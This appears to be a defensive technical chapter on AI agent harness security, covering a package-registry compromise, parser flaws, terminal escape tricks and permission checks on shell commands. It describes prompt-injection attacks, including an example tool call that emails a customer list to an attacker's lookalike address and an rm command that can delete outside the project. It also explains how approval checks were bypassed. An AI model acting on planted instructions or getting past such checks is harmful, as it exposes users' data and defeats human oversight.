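### The LiteLLM compromise

On March 24, 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM on PyPI, the main public registry of Python packages. The code searched each machine for passwords, login keys and cloud credentials, encrypted what it found and sent it to a server whose address resembled LiteLLM's own. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) traces the attack to Trivy, a security scanner that the project ran on its code before each release. Attackers had already compromised Trivy and used it to obtain the credentials to publish LiteLLM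 packages.

Reading LiteLLM's source on GitHub would not have revealed the attack. *Hardening Your LLM Dependency Supply Chain* points out that the attackers uploaded their packages directly to PyPI and the GitHub code stayed clean. The TCB of a program that uses LiteLLM therefore includes the registry and every account and tool that can publish a release. One of the two malicious versions also installed a file that Python processes whenever it starts, so its code could run even in programs that never used LiteLLM. The attackers only had to get their code onto a machine with something worth stealing, and did not need a flaw reachable from a prompt or a web page.

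Accounts of the scale differ. LiteLLM says the packages were available for about 40 minutes, and FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* counted 47,000 downloads in 46 minutes. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) reports more than 119,000 downloads over two hours and 32 minutes. Automated build systems download the same package repeatedly, so neither download count equals the number of victims.

Many of the victims got LiteLLM only as a dependency of other software. FutureSearch found 2,337 packages on PyPI that depended on it, and 88% of them had version requirements that allowed the malicious releases. LiteLLM's notice lists agent frameworks and tool servers among the software that could have installed it this way. PyPI compared downloads during the attack with the normal rate of about 1,700 a minute and estimated that 40 to 50% of LiteLLM installations take the newest version.

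Developers can avoid this by pinning, which means fixing the exact version of each package. LiteLLM's official container image pinned its dependencies, so its users were not affected. PyPI recommends lock files, which also record a checksum of each package so that the installer rejects an altered copy. It also suggests a waiting period, such as refusing packages less than three days old. The first report of the malicious LiteLLM packages came 79 minutes after the upload, so a one-day delay would have been enough.

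Pinning and waiting both hold back security fixes along with attacks. Ding and Stevens cite a study in which 81% of projects kept outdated dependencies, even after security warnings. PyPI therefore advises developers to combine the waiting period with a vulnerability scanner and let urgent fixes through early. But the scanner is then more code to trust, as LiteLLM's experience with Trivy shows. LiteLLM's *Security Update* on a later incident warns of a malicious version of Mistral AI's client library, which does a similar job to LiteLLM in an agent. The update tells anyone who installed and imported the malicious version to replace every credential on the machine.

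### Reviewing code that changes every day

A review applies to one version of a program, and harness developers release new versions often. Ben Sghaier and colleagues counted the releases of five open-source harnesses up to February 2026. OpenCode averaged 18 releases a week, Codex 12.4, Gemini CLI 10.3, Qwen Code 10 and OpenHands CLI 1.5. Microsoft's VS Code, a mature code editor of comparable complexity, averaged 0.8.

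These counts probably include many test builds that most users never install. For Qwen Code, the study lists 288 releases over about 29 weeks, but only 43 stable versions up to the last one it tested. Someone who installed only stable versions would still have received one or two a week, which is too often for an organisation that wants to examine each version before its staff use it. The study also shows a harness installing new trusted code through an automatic update, without the user's approval.

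Fast releases do not by themselves mean careless reviews. Most of the harness teams bundle 7 to 14 changes into each release, compared with about 420 for VS Code, and a small release is easier to check than a large one. VS Code's developers also merge about 48 changes a day, more than any of the five harness projects. Codex and OpenCode take a median of about three hours to review a proposed change, longer than VS Code's median of under an hour. OpenCode's backlog is a clearer sign of strain, as the project had closed only 54% of the issues that users reported, compared with 89% for VS Code.

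Automated tests are a weak substitute for reading the code. Ben Sghaier and colleagues ran 35 successive versions of Qwen Code with the same model and found several that solved fewer tasks or used more computation. Every change that they identified as the cause of a decline had passed the project's own tests. They also report that changes to security components rarely hurt quality, but they measured quality by bugs fixed and resources used. Saltzer and Schroeder's warning about testing applies to these measures too. A change that let the agent write outside its folder would not have lowered either score, because no task in the benchmark requires an agent to try.

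Barbaste and colleagues found that OpenAI sends Codex its prompts and some of its tool settings from a server, separately for each model. OpenAI can therefore change part of what the harness does without releasing a new version, even for users who keep an old one.

AI can also write and review a harness's code. Ben Sghaier and colleagues suspect that AI reviewers partly explain the short review times, since these projects are themselves coding agents, but they did not measure this. If one model writes a change to the permission checker and another approves it, model output, which the design treats as possibly hostile, becomes part of the code meant to contain the model. The harness's own controls would not catch this, because they check tool calls on the user's machine, and the change arrives in an update that the user has good reason to trust.

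Some harnesses let a model extend them on the user's machine by writing skills. A skill is a folder of instructions, sometimes with scripts, that an agent can load when a task needs it. Hermes has a background agent that writes new skills and revises old ones after finishing a task. Gemini CLI has a similar feature but puts the proposed skills in an inbox for a person to review. This lets a person decide whether the model's output affects the agent's later behaviour, but only if they read the skills before approving them.

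Model-written code can also make a harness smaller. Ding and Stevens used language models to write replacements for popular Python libraries, including web clients, data parsers and agent communication protocols. Each of the 44 replacements is a single file that needs only Python's standard library. Together they remove 88 transitive packages maintained by 128 PyPI accounts. A harness built on them would no longer depend on those accounts, so attackers would have fewer places to start an attack like the one on LiteLLM.

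It would depend instead on what the model wrote. Ding and Stevens test each file by running it and the original library on the same inputs and comparing the results. This catches ordinary mistakes, including many in unusual cases. It would miss a flaw that appears only on an untested input, which is the kind a hostile model would plant. Someone has to read the file to protect against that, which is realistic for the simplest replacements, typically under 200 lines, but much harder for the web client, which has more than 800.

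## Parsers that read the model's output

The parser, which turns the model's reply into a tool name and arguments, deserves more careful review than any other harness code. A permission checker checks only the parser's output, so its decisions all depend on the parser. But whoever steers the model also controls the parser's input.

An attacker who plants text on a web page can come close to writing the model's reply. *Terminal DiLLMa*, a December 2024 post on the security blog Embrace The Red, found that models can read unusual control characters and repeat them on request, so planted text can supply the exact characters the attacker wants. A model with a code-running tool can also generate them with a short program.

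Parsing often happens in two places. The company that hosts a commercial model finds the tool call in the model's raw output, and the harness then decodes the arguments. For a model that users run themselves, an inference server finds the tool call. vLLM, a widely used open-source server, has many parsers because model families write their tool calls in different formats.

### From tokens to a function call

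A model produces tokens, which are numbered pieces of text. Many models learn to put special markers before and after a tool call, and each marker usually has its own token number. Many parsers search for the markers only after the server has converted the numbers to text, when a real marker looks the same as one the model spelled out in ordinary characters. Even an honest model may therefore trigger an unintended tool call by quoting a web page that contains a look-alike marker.

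Parsers differ in how strict they are about this. vLLM's parser for DeepSeek-V3.1 stops with an error if the model's vocabulary lacks the two markers, although it still searches for them in the converted text. If the markers are missing in EasyDeL, another library for running models, its MiniMax parser logs a warning and matches plain text instead. A parser can also miss a real call. In vLLM's parser for Gemma 4, the expected markers did not match the converted text, so whole tool calls appeared as part of the answer and some argument values were garbled.

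The reply arrives in pieces, and the connection can break at any point. If a call has no closing marker, the DeepSeek parser accepts everything from the opening marker to the end of the text as the call. Another vLLM parser passes on long arguments character by character, because holding back a 4,000-character file until it was complete made users wait several seconds. The harness can safely display these partial arguments, but it is dangerous to act on them before they are complete. Joshi therefore lets only read-only calls start before the reply ends. But Joshi's harness still stored a reply as complete when the stream had closed without a finish reason.

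Next, the parser decodes the arguments, usually from JSON or XML, two formats for nested data. JSON uses curly braces to group values, but a brace can also appear inside a value, for example when the model writes source code. A search pattern in vLLM's Mistral parser failed to distinguish these two uses. When a developer proposed a simpler method, an automated reviewer on GitHub warned that the new code could crash if any text followed the arguments. A different fault in Meta's Llama Stack joined the arguments of separate tool calls into one.

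Two decoders that look correct can also disagree. If a JSON object contains the same name twice, some decoders keep the first value and others keep the last. If the permission checker and the tool use different kinds of decoder, the harness can approve one file path and write to another. A flaw in which two programs read the same input differently is called a parser differential. The simplest protection is to decode once and give the checker and the tool the same result.

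Each call also carries an identifier that links it to its result. According to Joshi, weak models sometimes leave identifiers blank or repeat them, and a retried reply can reuse identifiers from the abandoned attempt. These identifiers are therefore unsafe for matching a person's approval to a call, and the harness should assign its own.

The harness then checks the arguments and their types against the tool's schema. Some formats carry every value as text, so the parser must first convert the text "12" to the number 12. A mistake in this conversion can change a value after it has passed a check. MITRE's *CWE-150*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, advises developers to decode input fully before validating it and never to decode it twice.

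Finally, the harness looks up the tool by name and runs its code. This step, called dispatch, should refuse unknown names. Joshi also recommends testing nested arguments whose names the programming language reserves. Some tools then parse their arguments again. Barbaste and colleagues found that Aider, for example, supports thirteen formats for describing file edits.

Parsers change often, sometimes without new tests. In March 2026 a vLLM contributor found that several recent parser fixes lacked tests, including one for a crash on malformed XML. With the missing tests added, 510 parser tests passed and another 42 failed as expected, because they covered gaps the developers already knew about.

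### Running model text as code

The most serious parsing mistake is to run the model's text as a program. Python's `eval()` function runs text as Python code and returns the result. Developers sometimes use it to turn text such as "[1, 2, 3]" into a list, but if the text is code that deletes a file, `eval()` will run that too.

vLLM's parser for Qwen3-Coder, a model for programming tasks, used this shortcut. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2014* (2026) explains that the parser called `eval()` on arguments whose type the schema did not define or the parser did not recognise. Any logged-in user who could get the model to put code in such an argument could run it on the server. The flaw, CVE-2025-9141, has a severity score of 8.8 out of 10. It affected only servers that had turned on both tool calling and this parser. According to Wiz's *CVE-2025-9141*, the code entered vLLM in July 2025, and the project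 disclosed and fixed the flaw on August 20. An automated reviewer had flagged the call as a critical vulnerability before the maintainers accepted the change.

A year later, the same mistake turned up in Xinference, another program for running models. Averlon's *CVE-2026-61539* describes how Xinference passed tool calls from Llama 3 models to `eval()`. An attacker could exploit the flaw by sending a suitable prompt, without logging in. The flaw received the maximum severity score of 10.

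The consequences for an agent depend on where the server runs. If it runs on a separate machine, an attacker who takes it over can, like a malicious router, break a secrecy policy but not the file-writing rule. If a developer runs the server on the same laptop as the agent, the attacker's code can write wherever the server's account can, without making a tool call, so the parser belongs to the TCB even for the file-writing rule.

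A harness can also run model text as code on purpose. Barbaste and colleagues report that Codex can accept tool calls written as a program and run it in V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. The designers of such a system know that they are running untrusted code and can limit what it can reach. The developers of vLLM and Xinference thought they were reading data, so the code ran inside the server process with the server's full access.

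### Data that becomes an object

Programs often save complex objects as text (serialisation) and rebuild them later (deserialisation). Text from an attacker may cause the program to build an object the developer never intended. In LangChain, CVE-2025-68664 allowed this even in applications that only read back text they had saved themselves.

LangChain marks its own saved objects with a reserved key. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026), its saving functions did not check whether outside data already contained that key. When LangChain read back an attacker's data containing the key, it treated the data as one of its own objects and rebuilt it. An attacker could use this to read secrets such as login keys from environment variables. LangChain already restricted rebuilding to classes in its own packages, but an attacker could still create some of those objects with settings of their choice,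 including some that contact the network or open files when created.

The most common route was through extra fields attached to a model's response. A prompt injection could influence these fields, and some of LangChain's streaming functions then saved them and read them back. The attack could therefore work even if the developer never called a loading function or accepted a file from a stranger. Cyata, the security company whose researcher reported the flaw, describes the general error as treating "attacker-shaped data as trusted structure". OSV's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) gives the flaw a severity score of 9.3, and Docker's *CVE-2025-68665* describes the same flaw in LangChain's JavaScript version.

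The fix made LangChain treat the reserved key as ordinary data when it came from outside. LangChain also narrowed the list of objects it would rebuild by default, stopped loading secrets automatically and blocked a template language that can run code. These changes broke some existing applications but limited the damage any similar mistake could do.

They left some routes open. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2564* (2026) reports that some older functions still allowed every object on LangChain's full list. An attacker who could send structured data to an affected application could make LangChain rebuild it as chat messages and store them in the conversation history, where the model might later read them as genuine. The release that fixed this also closed a way around the earlier repair. The advisory tells developers not to use LangChain's loading functions as general parsers for tool inputs or chat messages.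 Applications that first reduce their input to plain text or a fixed schema are unlikely to be exposed.

### Patterns that take too long

Many parsers find tool calls with regular expressions, which are short patterns that describe text. Some patterns take a very long time on certain inputs. For example, a pattern might match one or more groups of one or more letters, and then a full stop. If the input is 30 letters with no full stop, a simple matcher may try every way of dividing the letters into groups before it reports that there is no match. Each of the 29 gaps between letters may or may not separate two groups, so there are 2<sup>29</sup> divisions, or about 537 million, and each extra letter doubles the work.

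OSV's *CVE-2025-48887* (2025) describes a pattern of this kind in a vLLM parser for Python-style tool calls. An attacker could use it to slow the server severely or make it unavailable. The flaw scored 6.5, lower than the others, because it did not expose data or let an attacker run code.

A stalled parser does not break a rule about file locations, but a stalled permission check might let a command break one if the harness runs the command anyway after a timeout. An attacker who can slow the check can then get past it, so the harness has to treat a timeout as a refusal. Developers can also avoid the problem by choosing a pattern-matching engine whose running time grows in proportion to the input's length.

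### Control characters in the terminal

A harness can cause harm even when the model makes no tool call, because it still has to display the answer. Terminals treat certain invisible characters as commands to change colours, move the cursor or clear the screen. Attackers have known about this since at least 1994, according to MITRE, and programs that print a model's answers have given them a new way to send these characters to a terminal.

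In one *Terminal DiLLMa* demonstration, a user asked a command-line tool to summarise a web page. Text on the page made the model include control characters in its summary, and the terminal changed colour, beeped and cleared its screen. In other tests, the model's output could place text on the user's clipboard, and in some terminals pasting that text ran it as a command. The output could also make Apple's Terminal look up an internet address containing data from the conversation, which leaked the data without the user clicking anything.

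*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* classifies this as a failure of complete mediation, because the output had effects that no check covered. The code that prints the answer is therefore part of the trusted computing base (TCB) for a secrecy policy.

Control characters can also deceive the person who approves an action. MITRE lists a case in which a program removed the control characters from the file name in its permission dialog but not from the name it used, so the user could grant access to a different file from the one shown. In Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025), a tool's reply hid a sentence from the user by colouring it white on white. The model could still read the sentence, which was about where to download Python software.

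Unsafe text can also come from sources other than the model. Claude HUD, a status display for Claude Code, printed the current folder's name and the code branch's address without removing control characters. According to Mondoo's *CVE-2026-47090*, a malicious folder or branch could use this flaw to display a forged prompt. The flaw's severity score was only 2.4, but a forged prompt is more serious in a program that relies on people's answers to decide what may run.

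MITRE recommends removing or neutralising control characters before printing a model's output, and rates this as highly effective. It rates removing them from the model's vocabulary lower, because a model might still assemble them from several tokens. Embrace The Red prefers to print them in a visible form, which is better for approval dialogs because the person can see that the name contains something unusual.

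### Recognising the whole input first

A field called language-theoretic security treats these flaws as one problem. Its central idea is that the set of inputs a program accepts is a language, whether or not anyone has written down its rules. The developer should define that language precisely, and the program should refuse any input outside it, checking the whole input before acting on any part.

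*CBCL* (2026) presents an agent message protocol built on these ideas, which it traces to work by Sassaman and colleagues. They observed that exploitable errors become more likely when the complexity of a language does not match the power of the parser that reads it. For example, a regular expression, in the strict mathematical sense, cannot track brackets nested to any depth, so a parser that uses one to find the end of a JSON object will fail on some inputs. Kaminsky, Patterson and Sassaman showed the practical danger with parser differentials, where two parsers read the same input differently, in the certificates that browsers use to identify websites.

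To apply this method to a tool call, the harness waits for the closing marker, decodes the entire call with one standard decoder, and rejects repeated names, unknown arguments and leftover text. It then checks every value against the schema and passes the result to the permission checker. Such a parser would not need `eval()`, because the language would contain only plain values such as numbers, text and lists.

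Writing a precise language by hand for each kind of message takes work. *Firewalls to Secure Dynamic LLM Agentic Networks* (2025) instead uses a language model to derive one from examples of harmless conversations between agents. A second model translates incoming messages into the language, and an ordinary program checks the result. An attacker may fool the translator, but the program still rejects any field or value that the language does not allow. The protection depends on the quality of the derived language, and a false statement that fits the permitted fields still gets through.

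Many harnesses repair malformed calls instead of rejecting them, because weak models often leave out a bracket or use the wrong kind of quotation mark, and a harness that refused every such call would finish fewer tasks. Joshi allows repair only when the call has exactly one possible reading, and requires that the repair never change its meaning.

A missing closing bracket is unambiguous only if the harness knows that the model's reply is complete. If a model calls a tool that deletes old files and the reply breaks off before the final bracket, adding the bracket produces valid JSON. But the model may have been about to add an argument that made the call a trial run, in which case the repaired call deletes files that the full call would only have listed.

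When the harness refuses a call, it can return an error that explains what was wrong, and the model can send a corrected call in its next reply. This adds only one step, and the harness never has to guess. If a model fails repeatedly, the harness can stop after a fixed number of attempts, as Joshi recommends for all such retries.

Some apparent weaknesses in models are faults in the software around them. A developer investigating why Kimi K2 often failed to make proper tool calls on vLLM found that most of the failures disappeared once he prepared the prompt outside the server. vLLM's *Chasing 100% Accuracy* explains that the server had been using the model's conversation template incorrectly. Repairing the malformed replies would have hidden the cause and added more code to trust.

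For an agent with access to valuable files, refusing a malformed call is a better default than repairing it. Repair is reasonable for a read-only tool, or when every later check runs on the repaired call and the person approving it sees that version.

### Forcing the model to follow a grammar

Constrained decoding prevents malformed calls instead of repairing them. At each step, a model assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary. A program called a grammar engine works out which tokens could come next in a valid call and sets the probability of all the others to zero. If the schema requires a number, the model cannot write a word. The resulting call fits the schema if the engine works correctly and the reply is not cut off.

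This guarantees the form of a call but not its purpose. Suppose a user asks an agent to email the October invoice to a bookkeeper, and a planted instruction leads the model to produce this call:

```json
{
  "tool": "send_email",
  "to": "accounts@bookkeeper.example",
  "body": "The October invoice is attached.",
  "attachment": "customer-list.csv"
}
```

The schema requires a valid email address, some text and the name of a file in the project folder. The call meets every requirement but sends the customer list to an attacker whose address resembles the bookkeeper's. A stricter schema could limit the address to the user's contacts, which would stop this attack, but the parser still could not check whether the user wanted to send that file.

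A call can be harmful even if the model does what the user asked. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that hostile data can corrupt a tool's arguments without the model following any planted instruction. If a forged invoice lists the attacker's bank account, an agent that copies the number into a payment form will pay the attacker. *CBCL* cites an argument by von Hippel and Miyazono that AI security is fundamentally a problem of language-theoretic security. The argument is persuasive for flaws like those in vLLM and LangChain, but no grammar can distinguish the correct account number from the attacker's when both have the same format.

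*How does `tool_choice` effect vllm?* explains that one vLLM setting makes the model produce at least one tool call instead of an ordinary answer. This can take away a safe choice, because a model that would otherwise have declined or asked a question has to call a tool.

The grammar engine also adds code that processes outside input, because it has to read each tool's schema, which may come from a tool server that someone else wrote. GitLab's *CVE-2025-48944* (2025) describes how a single request with a malformed schema could crash a vLLM worker, which then stayed down until someone restarted it. A bug report from July 2026, *tool_choice*, describes errors in the xgrammar grammar engine when a user forced a model to call a tool. The request failed with one tool and never finished with four.

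These failures only interrupt service. The risk is greater if the harness relies on the engine's guarantee and skips its own validation, because an error in the engine could then let a malformed call reach a tool. The TCB would then include the engine, the server it runs on, and any router that could alter the reply. If the harness validates every call again, they stay outside the TCB for a rule about file writes, and the extra check takes very little time.

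Even a correct grammar may cover only the outer layer of a request. The schema for a shell tool usually requires just a string, but that string is a program in another language, which the permission checker must parse before deciding whether to run it.

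## Permission checks on shell commands

A shell is a program that reads typed commands and starts other programs. Most coding agents use one, usually Bash, for tasks their built-in tools don't cover. The model proposes a command as a string of text, and the permission checker has to predict what the shell will do with it. Depending on that prediction, the harness runs the command, refuses it or asks a person. *One Goal, Many Commands* (Chen and Lin, 2026) describes the usual arrangement as three lists. A denylist blocks commands that should never run, an allowlist lets harmless ones run without approval, and everything else goes to the user or, in some harnesses, to a language model acting as judge.

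### Why commands are hard to predict

The shell rewrites a command before running it. Suppose the model proposes this clean-up step:

```sh
rm -r "$BUILD_DIR"/cache
```

To predict which folder the command will delete, the checker needs both the command's text and the value `$BUILD_DIR` will have when the command runs, because the shell substitutes that value first. If the variable holds the project's build folder, the command is harmless. If it is empty, the command deletes a folder called `cache` at the top level of the disk, outside the project.

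Other kinds of expansion are even harder to check. A command can contain a second command whose output becomes part of the first, and the checker can't determine that output without running the second command. A wildcard such as `*.txt` expands to the names of all matching files in the folder, and a program may treat an odd file name as an option. According to Anthropic's documentation, this is why Claude Code asks for permission before running certain search and editing programs with an unquoted wildcard.

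The shell treats `&&` as a separator between commands unless it is inside quotation marks. The command `echo "a && b"` prints the text `a && b`, while `echo a && b` runs `echo a` and then, if that succeeds, `b`. A permission checker that misjudges where a quotation ends can therefore mistake two commands for a single harmless one.

Even a permission check that parses a command perfectly cannot always determine what the command will do. The version-control program git mostly reads and records changes, but some options and configuration files make it start another program. The command `npm test` runs whatever test command the project's own files define, and the agent may have just edited those files.

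Most of these gaps are parser differentials, where the checker interprets a command differently from the shell or from the program that the shell starts. Decoding once is the remedy for tool arguments, but it does not work here as long as the harness passes the shell a string, because the shell will parse that string again.

Joshi suggests that a permission checker read commands strictly when approving them and loosely when refusing them. Approval requires establishing exactly what a command does, whereas refusal should catch anything that might be dangerous, even if the checker misreads some harmless commands. Claude Code does this for commands that begin by setting a variable. A rule that allows a program applies only if the variable is on a short list of safe ones, while a rule that denies the program applies whatever the variable is.

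### Five flaws in Claude Code

Between August 2025 and February 2026, public advisories described several flaws in how Claude Code checked commands. Anthropic has patched all of them.

CVE-2025-55284, published on August 18, 2025, resulted from an allowlist that covered too much. According to GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code's Permissive Default Allowlist Enables Unauthorized File Read and Network Exfiltration* (2025), an attacker could make Claude Code read a file and send its contents over the network without the user's confirmation. Version 1.0.4 fixed the flaw. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack of this kind, in which instructions hidden in a code file led the agent to read login keys and leak them through an allowed network command. The allowlist wrongly classed that command as safe with any arguments, so the flaw was a policy error, not a parser differential.

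The next flaw was a differential in the strict sense. A command could pass the check for read-only commands and then run arbitrary code. GitLab Advisory Database's *CVE-2025-66032* (2025), published on December 3, attributes the flaw to errors in parsing short options and a shell variable that controls how text is split into words. The flaw scored 8.8 out of 10 for severity, and version 1.0.93 fixed it.

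CVE-2026-24887 involved `find`, a program that searches for files but can also start other programs. GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code has a Command Injection in find Command* (February 3, 2026) reports that a parsing error let untrusted commands run through `find` without an approval request. Claude Code 2.0.72 fixed the error.

Two advisories followed on February 6. One of them, CVE-2026-25722, concerned commands that changed folder before writing a file. A relative path, such as `notes.txt`, refers to a different file after the change, so a checker has to track the current folder across commands. GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code Vulnerable to Command Injection via Directory Change Bypasses Write Protection* (2026) explains that Claude Code did not validate such changes properly, so commands could write to protected folders without approval. Version 2.0.57 fixed the flaw.

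CVE-2026-25723 involved pipes, which pass one program's output to another. GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code Vulnerable to Command Injection via Piped sed Command* (2026) reports that Claude Code failed to validate certain piped text-editing commands, so an attacker could write outside the project, which the file-writing rule forbids. An attacker could exploit the flaw only if the user had turned on the "accept edits" feature, and version 2.0.55 fixed it.

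The first four advisories all say that an attacker had to get untrusted text into the model's context to exploit the flaw reliably. Prompt injection exposed the checker by letting outsiders choose its input.

Besides these five, GitHub Advisory Database's *Claude Code echo command allowed bypass of user approval prompt* (2025) and *Claude Code rg vulnerability does not protect against approval prompt bypass* (2025) report two more errors in command parsing, both with a severity score of 8.7. The number of advisories is a poor basis for comparing Claude Code with its rivals, because a harness that runs most commands without asking has few approval requests to bypass, so researchers will find fewer flaws of this kind in it.

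Anthropic's current documentation lists many cases in which a normally harmless command still needs approval. Claude Code asks for approval if it can't fully parse the command, if the command is longer than 10,000 characters, or if the command changes to a different folder before running git. One check, complete only since version 2.1.290, covers an option that makes `ps` print other programs' environment variables, which may contain secrets. Each check depends on a specific behavior of a shell or program, so developers have to add more checks as people discover more such behaviors.

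### Patterns and syntax trees

Claude Code's permission rules are text patterns. A user who allows `npm test *` lets the agent run `npm test` with any arguments. Before matching, Claude Code splits chained commands and removes certain wrappers, such as `timeout`, which runs another command with a time limit. A chain can run without asking the user only if every command in it qualifies, and a single denied command blocks the whole chain.

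Patterns work best on the first few words of a command. Anthropic calls patterns that try to restrict arguments "fragile", because the same web address, for example, can appear after an option, inside a variable or behind a redirect. Anthropic also warns that a deny rule "isn't a security boundary around the program", since there are other ways to start the same program. Chen and Lin tested 1,709 public denylists, covering seven file operations. Depending on the operation, 69.0% to 98.6% of the lists meant to block it missed at least one command that performs it. Saltzer and Schroeder had this danger in mind when they advised designers to list what is permitted.

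Barbaste and colleagues found that OpenCode parses every shell command with tree-sitter, a library that turns program text into a tree showing how its parts fit together. The tree distinguishes a quoted `&&` from one that joins two commands, and it identifies the arguments of commands that handle files. OpenCode can then work out which files those arguments refer to and ask for permission before the agent touches anything outside the project.

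A syntax tree does not contain the values of variables or the output of other commands. Tree-sitter's grammar is also a separate description of the shell language, so it may differ from the shell that runs the command. OpenCode has changed its approach more than once. In July 2026, its documentation for version 2 described rules that matched the complete command string. It now documents rules that match each command a scanner extracts, and it offers an experimental scanner that replaces tree-sitter. If two scanners parse a command differently, the same rules can produce different results.

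The syntax tree also offers little protection unless the permission rules use it to stop commands. By default, OpenCode allows most actions and asks for approval mainly when a tool call involves files outside the project or repeats three times. It has no list of dangerous commands. An approved shell command runs with the user's own access to the computer, as OpenCode warns.

### Rules that carry their own tests

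Codex's rules compare lists of arguments. A rule names the first words of a command and the decision to apply, and its author can add examples:

```python
prefix_rule(
    pattern = ["npm", "test"],
    decision = "allow",
    match = ["npm test", "npm test --silent"],
    not_match = ["npm install"],
)
```

When Codex loads the file, it checks that the rule matches every example under `match` and none under `not_match`, so the author learns of a mistake before the rule takes effect. The rules are written in Starlark, a language similar to Python. OpenAI's *Rules* explains that the engine can run Starlark without side effects such as changes to files.

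The examples catch some mistakes in writing the policy, but only in cases the policy's author thought to include. Rashidi (2026), in *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, surveyed 39 papers and found that every enforcement mechanism in them assumes an honest policy author and leaves such mistakes unaddressed.

Codex splits a script into separate commands only if it consists of plain words joined by simple operators. If the script contains redirection, variables, wildcards or loops, Codex treats the whole script as a single request to run a shell. A rule that allows `npm test` then doesn't cover `npm test` inside that script. This makes approval cautious but weakens refusal, because a rule that forbids a program can't match it inside an unsplit script either. Something else, such as the sandbox or a person, then has to stop the program. A wrong approval is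 also high-stakes, because a Codex allow rule lets the command run outside the sandbox.

Harnesses also differ in how they resolve conflicting rules. Codex applies the strictest matching rule. Claude Code checks deny rules first, then rules that require asking the user, then allow rules, so a narrow permission can't create an exception to a broad prohibition. In OpenCode, the last matching rule wins, so a broad permission overrides any earlier prohibition on the same commands. Reviewers therefore have to read OpenCode's rules in order, including those from other settings files.

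### Hermes's list of dangers

Hermes, the large Python harness from Nous Research, has a 3,200-line approval module, about 32 times the length of mini-SWE-agent's core loop. According to Barbaste and colleagues, Hermes refuses commands that match any of twelve patterns for catastrophic actions, such as erasing a disk, even if the user has turned off approval requests. Another 47 patterns identify dangerous commands. Hermes matches them after undoing some common disguises, such as quotation marks in the middle of a word.

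To undo disguises, the harness has to imitate part of the shell, so its interpretation of a command can also differ from the shell's at this step. The larger weakness is that any command matching no pattern passes these checks. The patterns are useful against accidents, because a confused model is likely to write a destructive command in its usual form, but an attacker can keep looking for a form that the list doesn't cover.

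Hermes reads the setting that turns off approval requests once, when the module loads, so that a malicious skill can't change it later. It skips the dangerous-command checks for commands run in a container, unless the container can access a folder on the host.

### Approving only what the checker understands

Joshi's rule is stricter than any of these designs. A command may run without a person's approval only if the checker interprets every character exactly as every supported shell would. In practice, this limits automatic approval to a small grammar of command forms. A developer who adds a form also has to test near misses by inserting control characters and unusual spaces between its words and confirming that none of the altered commands runs without approval.

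The rule came from a mistake Joshi describes, in which a harness's developers wrote a simple parser to find command names and later relied on it to approve commands. In some cases, the parser and the shell ended a word at different places, so the shell interpreted a harmless-looking command as a different one.

Exact reading also covers the context in which a command runs. Joshi counts a git status check as read-only only if no option redirects git to another folder or configuration, the command line doesn't change folders, and neither the command nor the folder gives git an untrusted store of settings. Joshi's own harness, Crewroom, failed this item in his assessment. The rule is well argued, but there is no evidence yet that a full harness has met it.

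A harness can avoid much of the problem by asking the operating system to start a program directly, without a shell, and passing the arguments as a list, for example `["git", "status"]`. Nothing expands variables or wildcards, and `&&` is just another argument. The checker and the program receive the same list, so the remedy of decoding once applies again. *L3M*, the harness built for verification, bans shells.

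The checker still has to know what each program does with its options and configuration files. The harness also has to keep shells and language interpreters off the list of permitted programs, because their arguments can contain whole programs. The model can't use pipes, wildcards or redirection, so a search that takes one line in a shell may need several tool calls or a purpose-built tool.

The designs differ in how much work they hold up and how much code they add to the trusted computing base (TCB):

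| Design | Work refused or sent for approval | Trusted code added |
|---|---|---|
| Text patterns (Claude Code) | Commands outside the allow rules and the read-only set, or that the harness can't parse | Command splitter, wrapper list, and facts about many programs' options |
| Syntax tree (OpenCode) | Little under the default rules | Shell grammars and the library that runs them |
| Argument prefixes (Codex) | Allow rules for single commands don't cover complex scripts | Shell grammar, Starlark interpreter |
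| Danger patterns (Hermes) | Commands that resemble a known danger | 3,200-line module and an external scanner |
| Exact reading (Joshi) | Every unusual command, including harmless ones | A small grammar that must match every supported shell |
| Argument lists without a shell | Pipes, wildcards and redirection | Facts about each permitted program, but no shell parser |

None of these projects has published how many useful commands its checker blocks or delays, so the middle column can't be quantified. For an agent that reads text from strangers, argument lists are probably best where the task permits them, with exact reading elsewhere. Danger patterns are worth keeping as protection against accidents, but a security policy shouldn't depend on them.

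### What the person approves

A strict checker sends more commands to the user for approval, so the approval request is part of the check. In Anthropic's example from Claude Code, the request shows the description "Run the test suite", the command `npm test` and a notice that the command needs approval. The user can allow the command once, allow similar commands in future, switch to automatic review or refuse.

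The wording of a permission request can come from the model, the harness or, in Codex, the author of a rule, who can write a justification that may appear in the request. The person deciding should rely on the command itself and on words that the model can't influence. Joshi recommends scrolling to the end of a long command because the dangerous part might be off the screen.

Chen and Lin cite a figure from Anthropic that users accept 93% of requests, and conclude that people approve without thinking. But accepting 93% of requests would be reasonable if nearly all of them were harmless. It would be more useful to know how often people accept harmful requests, which the figure doesn't include. Still, users seldom refuse, so a designer should not assume that they will notice a rare dangerous command among many routine ones.

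Some harnesses use a model to review commands. Claude Code's auto mode uses a classifier, and Codex can have a second model review a request before it reaches the user. If the Codex reviewer times out or returns a malformed answer, the harness does not approve the command. Fatigue doesn't affect these models as it does human reviewers, but an attacker can try to influence them through the text they process. OpenHands has the agent's own model rate the risk of each action, which would be worthless alone if the model were hostile. But OpenHands can combine this rating with pattern checks and use the highest risk rating, so a falsely low rating from the model can't cancel a warning from the pattern checks.

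When a command needs approval and nobody is present to give it, the harness has to refuse the command. OpenCode rejects all approval requests when it runs without a user interface, and Claude Code does the same for background agents. A strict checker may therefore stop an overnight job because of one unusual but harmless command.

Standing approvals reduce the number of requests by covering future commands. If the user grants one for `npm test`, Claude Code saves the pattern `npm test *`, which applies to later sessions anywhere in the same repository. If the user approves a chain of commands this way, Claude Code saves a separate rule for each part that needed approval, up to five. It offers a standing approval only if it can show the user everything the approval would allow in the request. However, the pattern doesn't show what `npm test` will run after the agent edits the project.

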